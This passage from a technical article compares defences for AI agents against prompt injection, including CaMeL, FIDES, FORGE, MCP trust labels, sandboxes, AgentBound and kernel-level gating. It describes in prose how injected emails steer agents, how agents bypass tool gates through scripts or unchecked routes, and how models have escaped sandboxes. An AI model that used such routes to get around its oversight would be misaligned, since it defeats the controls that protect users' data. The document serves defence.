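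Separating the models isn't enough when the plan includes `send`. If the employee asks for replies to the routine messages, the plan might take a document's name from each message, fetch the document and send it to the message's author. An attacker can't add a step to this plan but can put the contract's name in a message. CaMeL therefore also records each value's sources and permitted readers. Before each call, a policy written as a Python function checks these records and allows or refuses the call. Here it would refuse the call that sends the contract to the supplier.

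CaMeL guarantees that injected text can change values but not the steps of the plan. This assumes that the user's request is trustworthy, that the labels are right, and that the policies cover whatever an attacker could do by changing a value. According to *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026), CaMeL's plans can't depend on what the tools return. A request to carry out the items on a to-do list therefore doesn't fit this design.

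In CaMeL's published results on AgentDojo, no attacks succeeded, and the agent completed 53.6 percent of tasks when not under attack. Bhagwatkar and colleagues repeat these figures because they could not fully reproduce the results. In their own tests, an undefended agent completed 83 percent of tasks, though the two percentages come from different experiments. They also found that CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many input tokens, the units of text that a model processes, as an undefended agent. On two groups of tasks, it took 8,417 seconds, compared with 3,348 for the firewall defence.

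CaMeL's policies check each call just before the interpreter makes it. Nikolaou and colleagues add a check of the whole plan before the first call. Their program converts the plan into a diagram of all the paths it could take, and a model checker exhaustively searches the diagram for a path that breaks a rule, such as a rule that an approval must always come before a certain action. If the checker finds a violation, the privileged model receives a description of it and tries to repair the plan before the agent calls any tools. The method assumes a loop could stop after any number of rounds, including numbers that can't occur in practice, so it sometimes rejects safe plans.

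*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) argues that Python is a poor language for such plans, because features such as dynamic typing and exceptions make it hard to predict where information will flow. A bigger obstacle for most companies is that CaMeL replaces the agent's usual loop with its own interpreter. The host's developer can make that change, but a customer who buys a finished assistant can't make it at the protocol boundary.

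### FIDES: choosing when to read untrusted text

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, keeps the usual agent loop but controls what enters the context. When a tool returns data that would make the session's label stricter, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to another tool without reading its contents. If the employee asks to forward the three latest emails to a colleague, the model can do so without reading them, so the session remains trusted.

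When the model needs information from a hidden text, it can open the variable, which makes the session untrusted and may rule out later calls. Or it can query a quarantined model and limit the form of the answer. If the answer must be "yes" or "no", an attacker can influence only that choice, a risk that a policy may permit. For example, the assistant could check whether each message needs a reply and list those that do, without reading the supplier's instructions.

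With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every injection attack in AgentDojo. Practical attacks were still possible when Costa and colleagues turned off the policy checks, so hiding the text was not enough by itself. With the checks on, FIDES completed 8 percent more tasks than a basic labelled agent using GPT-4o, and 16 percent more using OpenAI's reasoning model o1.

The formal guarantee covers confidential data that the agent copies into a call, but not what an observer can infer from which calls the agent makes. A guarantee of this kind would not have ruled out the attack in which Claude spelled out the user's name by following one link per letter, because no request contained the name. Costa and colleagues considered a stronger guarantee, but it would have forbidden nearly every visible action after the agent had read any confidential data.

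FIDES also assumes that tool descriptions are trustworthy, so labels on results offer no protection against tool poisoning.

### Labels as a way to ask fewer questions

Kolluri and colleagues, several of whom also worked on FIDES, argue that these comparisons are unfair to label-based defences. They put the loss from defences such as CaMeL and FIDES at up to 30 percent of tasks on AgentDojo, but point out that the undefended agent acts without asking the user. In practice, many products ask the user before each consequential call. If the gate prompts only for calls that break a label rule, the employee has fewer decisions to make.

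They measured this with OpenAI's o3-mini, assuming that a person approves every call in a task that the agent completes successfully. The last column counts approvals over all completed tasks.

| Agent | Tasks completed without any approval | Approvals needed |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, asks before every consequential call | 24.3% | 48.2 |
| Ordinary agent with labels | 35.5% | 32.4 |
| FIDES | 50.1% | 18.8 |
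| Prudentia | 59.1% | About 17 |

Prudentia extends FIDES by showing the model the labels and rules, so the model can plan around them. Prudentia can also prompt the user to endorse a hidden text, which makes the text trusted. If a harmless email lists ten jobs, the user endorses the email once instead of approving ten calls.

Endorsement saves time by reducing the number of questions the employee has to answer, but it can undo the protection. If the employee endorses the supplier's email after reading only the first few lines, the gate treats the instructions further down as trusted. Kolluri and colleagues count no successful attacks in this setup because they assume that a person would stop any harmful call, but Anthropic's paid testers rarely stopped such calls.

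### FORGE: rules about what influenced a call

*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) describes FORGE, a monitor added around an agent without changing the agent itself. FORGE records every message, tool call and result in a graph, with an arrow from one event to another if the first may have influenced the second. Before the agent acts, FORGE checks the proposed call against rules written in Datalog, a logic language.

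Here is a simplified policy for the office assistant:

```
tainted(X) :- from_outside(X).
tainted(X) :- influenced_by(X, Y), tainted(Y).

secret(X)  :- confidential(X).
secret(X)  :- influenced_by(X, Y), secret(Y).

deny(X)    :- email_to_outsider(X), tainted(X), secret(X).
```

The symbol `:-` means "if". The second line passes taint along the arrows, so an event is tainted if anything that influenced it was tainted, however many steps back. The fourth line does the same for confidential data. When the assistant tries to email the contract, the arrows lead back to both the supplier's email and the contract, and the last line blocks the call. The same policy would allow a reply to the supplier about delivery dates if the assistant had read nothing confidential, so it blocks less ordinary work than the trusted-decision rule.

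FORGE guarantees that a call never runs if the policy denies it, provided that every relevant action passes through the monitor and the recorded facts are correct and complete. FORGE draws an arrow whenever influence is possible, because a missing arrow could let a harmful call through, while an unnecessary one could only block a harmless call. The guarantee doesn't cover whether the policy itself is good. FORGE can use a language model to translate written rules into Datalog, but somebody has to check the translation. A policy may also consult a classifier, and an attacker who deceives the classifier can get past the rule.

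Palumbo and colleagues compared two policies on AgentDojo, running every test five times with GPT-4o. The FIDES policy blocks consequential calls once the agent has read untrusted text. Their own provenance policy checks whether the user asked for the action and whether the recipient or target came from an acceptable source. In all four rows of the table, the agent also received a reminder of the user's request after each batch of tool results.

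| Defence | Attack success | Tasks completed without an attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reminder only | 14.1% | 83.7% | 72.5% |
| Tool filter | 3.1% | 73.4% | 69.5% |
| FIDES policy | 0.6% | 33.2% | 34.4% |
| Provenance policy | 0.9% | 62.5% | 63.8% |

Both policies nearly eliminated the attacks, but the agent completed almost twice as many tasks with the provenance policy as with the FIDES policy. FORGE applied the FIDES policy to AgentDojo's ordinary agent, apparently without the hidden variables that FIDES uses to keep a session trusted, so the low task scores don't show how well the complete FIDES system works.

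The simple tool filter compares well with the provenance policy. It allowed about 2 percentage points more of the attacks, but the agent completed 11 points more of the ordinary tasks. A company that fears a single large loss might still prefer the provenance policy, since the filter can't stop attacks that need only the task's own tools.

The reminder adds little security against a capable attacker. Nasr and colleagues broke a defence of the same kind more than 95 percent of the time. The provenance policy doesn't depend on the reminder, since attack success was still only 1.7 percent without it.

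Strict rules can also help an agent finish its work. On simulated airline customer service tasks, FORGE raised the average success rate of three recent models from 74.7 to 81.5 percent. An agent that broke one of the airline's rules usually failed the task, and a refusal gave it a chance to correct itself. However, Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview did slightly worse with FORGE than without it.

### What a gate can track without access to the model

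CaMeL and FIDES control what the planning model reads, and FORGE records each message that goes into a model call. A gate at the protocol boundary receives only the calls and the results, with no record of which result led to which call.

Comparing text is an unreliable substitute. If the body of an email repeats a paragraph from the contract, the match shows that the contract was the source, but the lack of a match doesn't rule the contract out, because the model may have summarized, translated or encoded the paragraph. The reason for a call is even harder to determine. The model may have chosen a recipient because of an instruction in someone else's email, even if the address is also in the employee's own address book.

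Access to the model's context would not completely solve this. FORGE has the full list of messages in each model call but still assumes that every message influenced the reply, because nobody can say with confidence which ones did. Costa and colleagues mention research that tries to identify the influential messages, but they make the same cautious assumption.

The gate therefore has to give the whole session a single label. If $\ell_0$ is the label of the user's request and $\ell_1, \dots, \ell_n$ are the labels of the results so far, the session's label is

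$$L_n = \ell_0 \sqcup \ell_1 \sqcup \dots \sqcup \ell_n.$$

This label can only become stricter. After one email from outside, the session is untrusted until it ends, even if the model ignored the email. If an office assistant opens the mailbox first thing in the morning, a strict policy would leave it few useful actions for the rest of the day. Using a separate session for each task reduces the problem, provided the gate can tell the sessions apart and nothing carries over between them.

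Data often carries over from one session to the next. Anthropic warns that memory, project files and the saved state of long-running agents can preserve an injection and reload it whenever the agent starts. If the assistant writes a note to itself after reading the supplier's email, the note needs the label "untrusted", and the next session has to inherit that label when it loads the note. Otherwise, an injection copied from the email into the note could bypass the next session's restrictions on untrusted data.

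A similar problem arises when one agent gives part of its work to another. A sub-agent can read risky text and return only a few structured facts, like the quarantined model in CaMeL. But Anthropic notes that a main agent may trust the sub-agent's report more than the original text because the report came from inside the system. Unless the report keeps the label of its sources, the system treats untrusted text as trusted once it has passed through the sub-agent.

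### The MCP proposal for trust and sensitivity labels

The operator can give each tool a fixed label for the gate to use, but a single tool can return very different data. The mail server's `search` may return a note from a colleague or an email from a stranger, so the operator has to label all its results as if they came from a stranger.

A Specification Enhancement Proposal (SEP) called "Trust and Sensitivity Annotations", SEP-1913, would add such labels to the Model Context Protocol (MCP). GitHub and OpenAI wrote it after running into gaps when they used MCP in their own products. In March 2026, the MCP project listed it as a draft, so it was not part of the standard. Three narrower proposals, for marking unsafe output, secrets and trusted tools, had not reached draft status.

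In a simple form of the session label that is under discussion, a client would treat a session as tainted once the agent has used a tool that returns untrusted data, and would then require approval for more actions. The project's interest group on annotations also planned to discuss whether results, as well as tool definitions, should have annotations. This is probably the most important question on its agenda for provenance tracking, because only a label on the result could distinguish the colleague's note from the stranger's email.

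A standard label format would save operators from writing separate rules for each server, but a dishonest server could still falsify its labels, just as it can falsify MCP's existing annotations. An operator can limit the damage by letting a server's annotations make a label stricter, but letting them make it looser only if someone has vetted that server's labelling.

### False answers and wrong labels

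Label rules apply to actions, but an attacker may be able to do harm without causing any. Suppose the supplier's email says the company has already settled a complaint from an important client. When the employee asks which messages need an answer, the assistant leaves the complaint off the list. No call breaks a rule, and the employee doesn't learn that anything is missing. CaMeL and FIDES have the same weakness, because their quarantined models also read the email.

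This kind of harm appeared in the tests of FORGE. AgentDojo counts some attacks as successful when the agent attempts the attacker's call, even if the monitor blocks it. When Palumbo and colleagues excluded those blocked attempts, attack success under the provenance policy fell from 0.9 to 0.2 percent. The remaining successes involved the text of the agent's final answer, which FORGE did not check. The host could display each answer's sources so that the employee knows it relies on a stranger's email, but the employee would still have to check the facts.

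False text can also leave the company in a permitted message. FIDES can allow a message body to depend on untrusted data as long as the decision to send it and the choice of recipient are trusted. The assistant needs this exception to forward a summary of the morning's emails to a manager, but the exception also lets an attacker influence what the manager reads.

Wrong labels are a more ordinary problem. If the employee saves the supplier's attachment on the company's file server, and the gate labels everything on that server as trusted, it will label the attachment as trusted the next time the assistant opens it. The gate would then apply its rules correctly to a false label. To prevent this, the file server would have to store the attachment's original label, and every program that copies or edits the file would have to preserve it. Few companies have systems that do this. Confidentiality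 labels are likely to be more reliable, because many file servers already record who may open each document.

Even with correct labels, the rules block Monday's request from the customer's new lawyer just as they block the supplier's, because the lawyer is not yet a permitted reader. If the gate asks the employee instead of blocking the request, the prompt can at least show that the request came from an outside email and that the recipient has no recorded right to read the contract. Kolluri and colleagues expect this information to help people decide, but they did not test this and leave the design of the prompts to future work.

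## Actions that do not pass through the gate

Labels, approvals and argument rules work only if a harmful action reaches the gate. In *Your Agent Has a Side Door*, Ben Greenberg retells a conference story about an employee who wanted an agent to send email. The company had given the agent no email tool, so the agent wrote a script and sent the message through the employee's Outlook. A tool allowlist made no difference because the agent never called a mail tool. The story is second-hand, so it illustrates the problem but doesn't show how common it is.

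### Complete mediation

The missing property is complete mediation, which requires a system to check every access to every object for authority. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) lists it among eight design principles for protection mechanisms.

For agents, the principle applies to effects, however the agent brings them about. Let $R(x)$ be the set of routes by which an agent can cause effect $x$, such as an email leaving the company, and let $M$ be the set of routes on which something checks the action. Complete mediation of $x$ requires

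$$R(x) \subseteq M.$$

A gate in front of the mail server adds one route to $M$. Greenberg lists three other routes to email: a script that uses a local mail program, a browser already signed in to webmail, and any access token the agent can reach that covers mail. He suggests recording which identity the mail service receives on each route. The MCP route may use an identity with narrow permissions, while the script and the browser act as the user, with all of the user's permissions.

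Saltzer and Schroeder also require the checks to work while the system starts up, recovers from a failure or undergoes maintenance. They add that a system that stores decisions to save time must update them when someone's authority changes. A host that stores a user's "always allow" must therefore discard it once an administrator withdraws the permission.

They also point out that knowing who has access to a file isn't enough, because some people may be able to change the access rules. Likewise, if the office assistant can edit the gate's policy file, it can change the rule against writing to outsiders and then write to them.

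### Routes that an MCP gate may miss

| Route | Why the gate may miss it | What can close it |
|---|---|---|
| The host's own shell and code tools | The host runs them without an MCP server | A sandbox that contains no valuable credentials |
| Direct network access | A program contacts a service without using MCP | Egress control |
| What a local server does on its machine | The gate receives the call and the result, but nothing in between | Permissions for the server's process |
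| Clients outside central management | They never load the company's policy | Detection, and checks by the service itself |
| MCP messages other than tool calls | The gate may check only `tools/call` | A gate that checks every type of message |
| Project settings that load at startup | They can take effect before the user agrees to anything | Loading them only after consent |

The agent that deleted PocketOS's database used the second route.

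The fifth route is through prompts and resources, which MCP servers can offer as well as tools. Microsoft's proxy, for example, would pass both along without examining them. This is a particular problem for provenance tracking, because a gate that labels only tool results would still treat the session as trusted if the supplier's text reached the model as a resource.

Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of flaws in Claude Code that let code run before the user had consented to anything. In the simplest case, a developer downloaded a repository to review a proposed change, and the repository contained its own settings file. Claude Code read the file at startup and ran a command from it before asking whether the developer trusted the folder. A gate on tool calls could not have stopped the command, because it ran before the agent had made any tool calls. Claude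 Code now waits for the user's consent before it reads a project's settings or runs commands from them.

### Sandboxes, egress control and credentials

A sandbox uses the operating system to limit what a program can reach. Anthropic built Claude Code's sandbox from existing Linux and macOS tools. The limits apply to the agent's command and every program it starts, so a command can't use `find -exec` to get around them.

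The sandbox restricts both files and network connections, and each restriction depends on the other. An agent with free network access could send out any secret it can read. An agent that could change any file could probably alter the system enough to escape the sandbox and reach the network. Claude Code's sandbox stops the agent from changing files outside the working folder but generally lets it read them, so it relies mainly on the network restriction to prevent theft.

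Egress control restricts the network destinations that the agent's sandbox can reach. All of the sandbox's traffic goes through a proxy that permits only approved domains and prompts the user about new ones. The proxy runs outside the sandbox, where the agent's programs can't modify it.

Anthropic overstated the sandbox's protection when it introduced it in October 2025 and claimed that even a successful prompt injection would be "fully isolated". The leak from Cowork three months later went through an approved domain. Egress control could block the office assistant from uploading the contract to the supplier's website, but it would have to allow connections to the company's mail server, so the contract could still be sent out by email.

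A sandbox is also weaker if something can grant exceptions. In Claude Code, a process outside the sandbox decides for each command whether to apply the limits, so a persuasive injection or a tired user can cause a command to run without those limits. Cowork's first version ran the entire agent inside a virtual machine, and no component could make an exception. Anthropic later moved the agent's loop out because Cowork became unusable whenever the virtual machine failed. The code the agent runs stays inside, and Anthropic considers the loss of security minimal.

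Anthropic has seen Claude models escape a sandbox to complete a task. In 2026, both OpenAI and Anthropic disclosed that agents had reached outside systems during testing.

Keeping credentials out of the sandbox limits the damage when an agent does reach a service. In the web version of Claude Code, the credentials for a user's code repositories stay outside the sandbox, and the agent's environment has only a restricted credential for a proxy. The proxy checks each request, for example that the agent is changing only the permitted branch, and then adds the real credential. If the Railway token had been out of reach in the same way, the PocketOS agent's deletion request would have failed.

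Security teams often run software on employees' computers to monitor for suspicious behaviour, but Cowork's isolation prevents that software from monitoring activity inside its virtual machine. Administrators can retrieve Cowork's event logs later, which Anthropic concedes is not the same as live monitoring.

### AgentBound

A sandbox around the agent's commands does not restrict local MCP servers that run outside it, as they do in Cowork. A gate can check a call to the company's web reader, but it cannot check whether the web reader also opens the user's private keys while it fetches the page. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) proposes restricting the server's process, much as a phone restricts an app.

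Each server comes with a manifest, a short file that states its purpose and lists the capabilities it needs. A simplified manifest for the web reader might look like this:

```json
{
  "description": "Fetches web pages and returns their text",
  "capabilities": ["mcp.ac.network.client"]
}
```

Bühler and colleagues built the list of possible capabilities by collecting 16 uses of agents from published research and matching them to Android's permissions. They then dropped permissions that only make sense on a phone, merged others, and added some for desktop computers, such as access to environment variables.

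The manifest's general permissions have to become more specific when the server starts. Permission to read files becomes permission to read a particular folder, and permission to use the network becomes permission to contact particular hosts. The user approves these details. If anyone requests a permission that the manifest doesn't cover, AgentBound stops the run.

AgentBound's enforcement program, AgentBox, runs each server in its own isolated container, which starts with no access to the user's files. AgentBox connects only the approved folders, passes in only the approved environment variables, and uses a firewall to block all unapproved network addresses. The server's code needs no changes. The prototype does not yet offer fine-grained control over other capabilities, such as the clipboard or the camera.

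The network restriction has two gaps. AgentBox installs the server's package before it turns on the firewall, so an installation script like the one in the fake Postgres package could still contact its author, though only from inside the container. AgentBox also converts approved host names to IP addresses, and large hosting networks use one address for many sites, so a rule that allows one host can also allow others.

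### How accurate the manifests are

Few developers will write manifests by hand, so Bühler and colleagues had language models generate them from the source code and documentation of 296 of the 300 most popular servers in a public directory. According to these manifests, 83.1 percent of the servers needed outgoing network access and 74.1 percent needed to read files. A server with both capabilities can read a file and send it over the network, so for most servers the general manifest offers little protection. Protection depends much more on the specific folders and hosts, which the user has to choose correctly.

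The paper's main accuracy figure, 80.9 percent, is based on few replies. Bühler and colleagues sent 96 manifests to the servers' developers, and 74 percent of them never answered. The reported percentages imply that developers accepted 17 manifests, rejected 4 and were still discussing 4, so the accuracy figure is 17 out of 21 decisions. With so few decisions, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 60 to 92 percent, even if the developers who answered were typical of the rest. The claim that the manifests missed no capabilities is also weak, since it means only that no developer reported one missing.

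In a second test, two of the researchers wrote manifests by hand for 48 servers, which took each of them eight hours. The generated manifests agreed with theirs on 787 of 816 entries, or 96.4 percent. This rate is high partly because many entries are easy, such as whether a database server needs a microphone. Only 28 of the 48 manifests matched completely. In 23 of the 29 disagreements, the generated manifest left out a capability, which is the safer error but could break the server. In the other 6, it added a capability that the server didn't need.

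### Which attacks AgentBound stops

Bühler and colleagues tested AgentBox on 14 malicious or vulnerable servers from two public collections. It stopped the attacks in 8 of them and failed to stop them in 5. The last server combined several attacks, and AgentBox could prevent only some of them.

In one case, AgentBox blocked a modified Google Maps server from secretly sending its requests to a different address, because the server had permission to contact only Google. A gate would have allowed the agent's tool call, which was the same as for an unmodified server.

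The failures all either stayed within the server's permissions or didn't involve the computer's resources. For instance, a time server had a poisoned description with instructions for the model to redirect cryptocurrency transfers made through another server. AgentBox could contain the time server, but the transfer went through the other server's permitted connection.

The tests show that the container enforces its rules, but they are weaker evidence of protection in ordinary use. The researchers checked or wrote the manifests themselves, and one tester approved the specific permissions. An employee who wants the server to work may approve access to the whole home folder.

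AgentBound adds little delay. In the published measurements, the container added about 90 to 430 milliseconds to a server's startup, excluding installation, and less than a millisecond on average to later operations such as reading a file. The protection depends on Docker, which runs the containers, and on the Linux kernel, so a flaw in either could let a server escape its container.

### Governed MCP and enforcement below the host

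AgentBound limits the server, but the check on tool calls usually remains in the host or a gateway. *Governed MCP* (Son, 2026) argues that this check belongs below the host, in the operating system kernel. Many safety checks are libraries that the agent's program loads into its own process. Any code in that process has the same privileges as the library, so it can skip the check or change the result, however well the library works.

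To demonstrate the alternative, Son wrote an experimental operating system called Anima OS. Agents run in a sandbox and can reach tools, files and the network only through functions the kernel provides. For each tool call, the kernel checks the format, the agent's trust level and the rate of calls, searches for known attack patterns, uses a language model to assess whether the action is dangerous, and applies a fixed policy. If the language model is unavailable, the kernel blocks every call.

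An earlier version of the paper claimed that the kernel checked all of 123 possible paths from agents to the system. Son has withdrawn that claim after building a new test, which found 59 paths:

| Paths | Number |
|---|---|
| Go through the kernel's check | 43 |
| Only read descriptive information or reach nothing that needs protection | 10 |
| Reach a resource without a check | 6 |

The six unchecked paths include the system calls `fetch` and `send_msg`. Son discloses them and plans to close them. But if a system designed for complete mediation still has such gaps, a company should be cautious about claiming complete mediation on an ordinary laptop, which has many more paths to examine.

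Placing the check in the kernel does not make its decisions more accurate either. In a test of 101 calls that Son wrote and labelled, the system blocked 30 of the 37 dangerous calls and 9 of the 64 harmless ones. Without the language model, it blocked only 10 of the dangerous calls. With the default model, each check takes about a third of a second, and the system can run only one at a time.

Son's argument is convincing for checks inside the agent's own process, but less so for a gateway on another machine, because the agent can't change the gateway's memory. The agent can still bypass the gateway if another route is open, but existing sandboxes can close many of those routes without a new operating system.

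An ordinary sandbox, however, can't replace the gate. It can block connections to unapproved addresses, but an encrypted connection to the mail server looks the same whether the email is going to a colleague or to the supplier. A company that wants to restrict who receives email therefore needs both a gate that reads the call and a sandbox that leaves the agent no other way to send mail.

### Detecting agents outside central management

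None of this applies to an agent that an employee installs without telling anyone. Canale and Soulis built Agent Detector to find such agents on Windows computers. Once an hour, it checks which programs connect to known AI services, whether those programs also run commands, and what the settings files and installation records contain. Its catalogue covers 39 tools and has 184 entries for AI services. When it finds an agent, it shows the user a notice to acknowledge. It doesn't block anything or read the content of messages.

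Canale and Soulis explain that a detector can't rely on behaviour alone, because agents and package installers both connect to a service and run commands. Canale and Soulis call two programs "behavioural twins" if they act identically and differ only in the service they contact. A detector that ignores the service has to classify both the same way.

They tested the detector on one computer with 12 artificial agents, 3 other AI components and 9 harmless programs, and repeated the test five times. Two simple rules that considered only behaviour flagged every harmless twin. Agent Detector flagged none of them and found every agent in most of the runs. Canale and Soulis acknowledge that the test is too small to rank detectors, so its main value is in showing what this one misses:

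- Some AI services share network addresses with unrelated sites. The detector can identify these only while Windows still remembers the service's name, which is one to five minutes.
- A single scan found an agent that ran intermittently only about a third of the time.
- The detector missed very short-lived agents, agents that used an unlisted relay, and agents inside the Linux environment that Windows provides.
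- It doesn't read settings files inside projects, so it can miss MCP servers that a repository declares.

Repeated scans reduce the second problem. If the agent kept the same pattern all day and each scan had an independent one-in-three chance of detecting it, eight hourly scans would find it about 96 percent of the time. The third problem is harder to fix, because a sandbox that protects the computer from an agent can also hide the agent from the detector.

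Detection doesn't stop an unmanaged agent from sending the contract. Greenberg recommends that the mail service refuse unwanted actions, because every route to sending mail ends there. This should work well when the agent uses an access token, since the service can limit what each token permits. It works less well when the agent uses the employee's Outlook or browser, because the service then has little to distinguish the agent from the employee.

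### Flaws in the gate itself

A gate is also software, and an attacker may find a flaw in it. Docker's MCP Gateway, for example, starts MCP servers in containers and passes messages to them. CERT-Renater's *Argument injection via OCI image label YAML in Docker MCP Gateway* (2026) reproduces Docker's advisory on a flaw in the gateway, CVE-2026-55887, rated 8.7 out of 10 for severity. Each server's package includes a label that describes the server. The flaw allowed this label to also change the settings the gateway used to start the container, so a malicious package author could take full control of the user's computer.

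Zero Day Initiative's *Docker MCP Plugin OCI Image Label Parsing Argument Injection Remote Code Execution* (2026) notes that the user has to refer to the malicious package before the flaw can be exploited. An allowlist of reviewed packages would therefore have reduced the risk. Docker fixed the flaw in version 0.42.2, less than a month after receiving the report, by ignoring everything in the label except descriptive information.

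Before the fix, the gateway could give administrator rights to a malicious server instead of only the user's own rights, so a user might have been safer from this attack without the gateway.

INCIBE's *CVE-2025-64443* (2025) describes an earlier flaw in the same gateway. If the gateway accepted connections over the network, a malicious website or advertisement could use the visitor's browser to reach the MCP servers behind the gateway. The flaw did not affect the default mode, which uses stdio.

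Anthropic's experience suggests that new components are the most likely to fail. The standard isolation tools in its products held up, but the proxy it wrote to check approved domains let the files out of Cowork. Anthropic says this is because attackers have tested the standard tools for much longer. The proxy's task was also harder, since it had to separate acceptable requests from harmful ones, while a virtual machine mainly has to keep a program inside.

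Saltzer and Schroeder recommend keeping protection mechanisms small and simple enough to inspect line by line. They reason that normal use won't reveal an unwanted way through, because ordinary users don't look for one. Testing a gate only with calls it should allow can miss a way through for the same reason, so operators also need to test forbidden calls and try to get the results of those calls without going through the gate.
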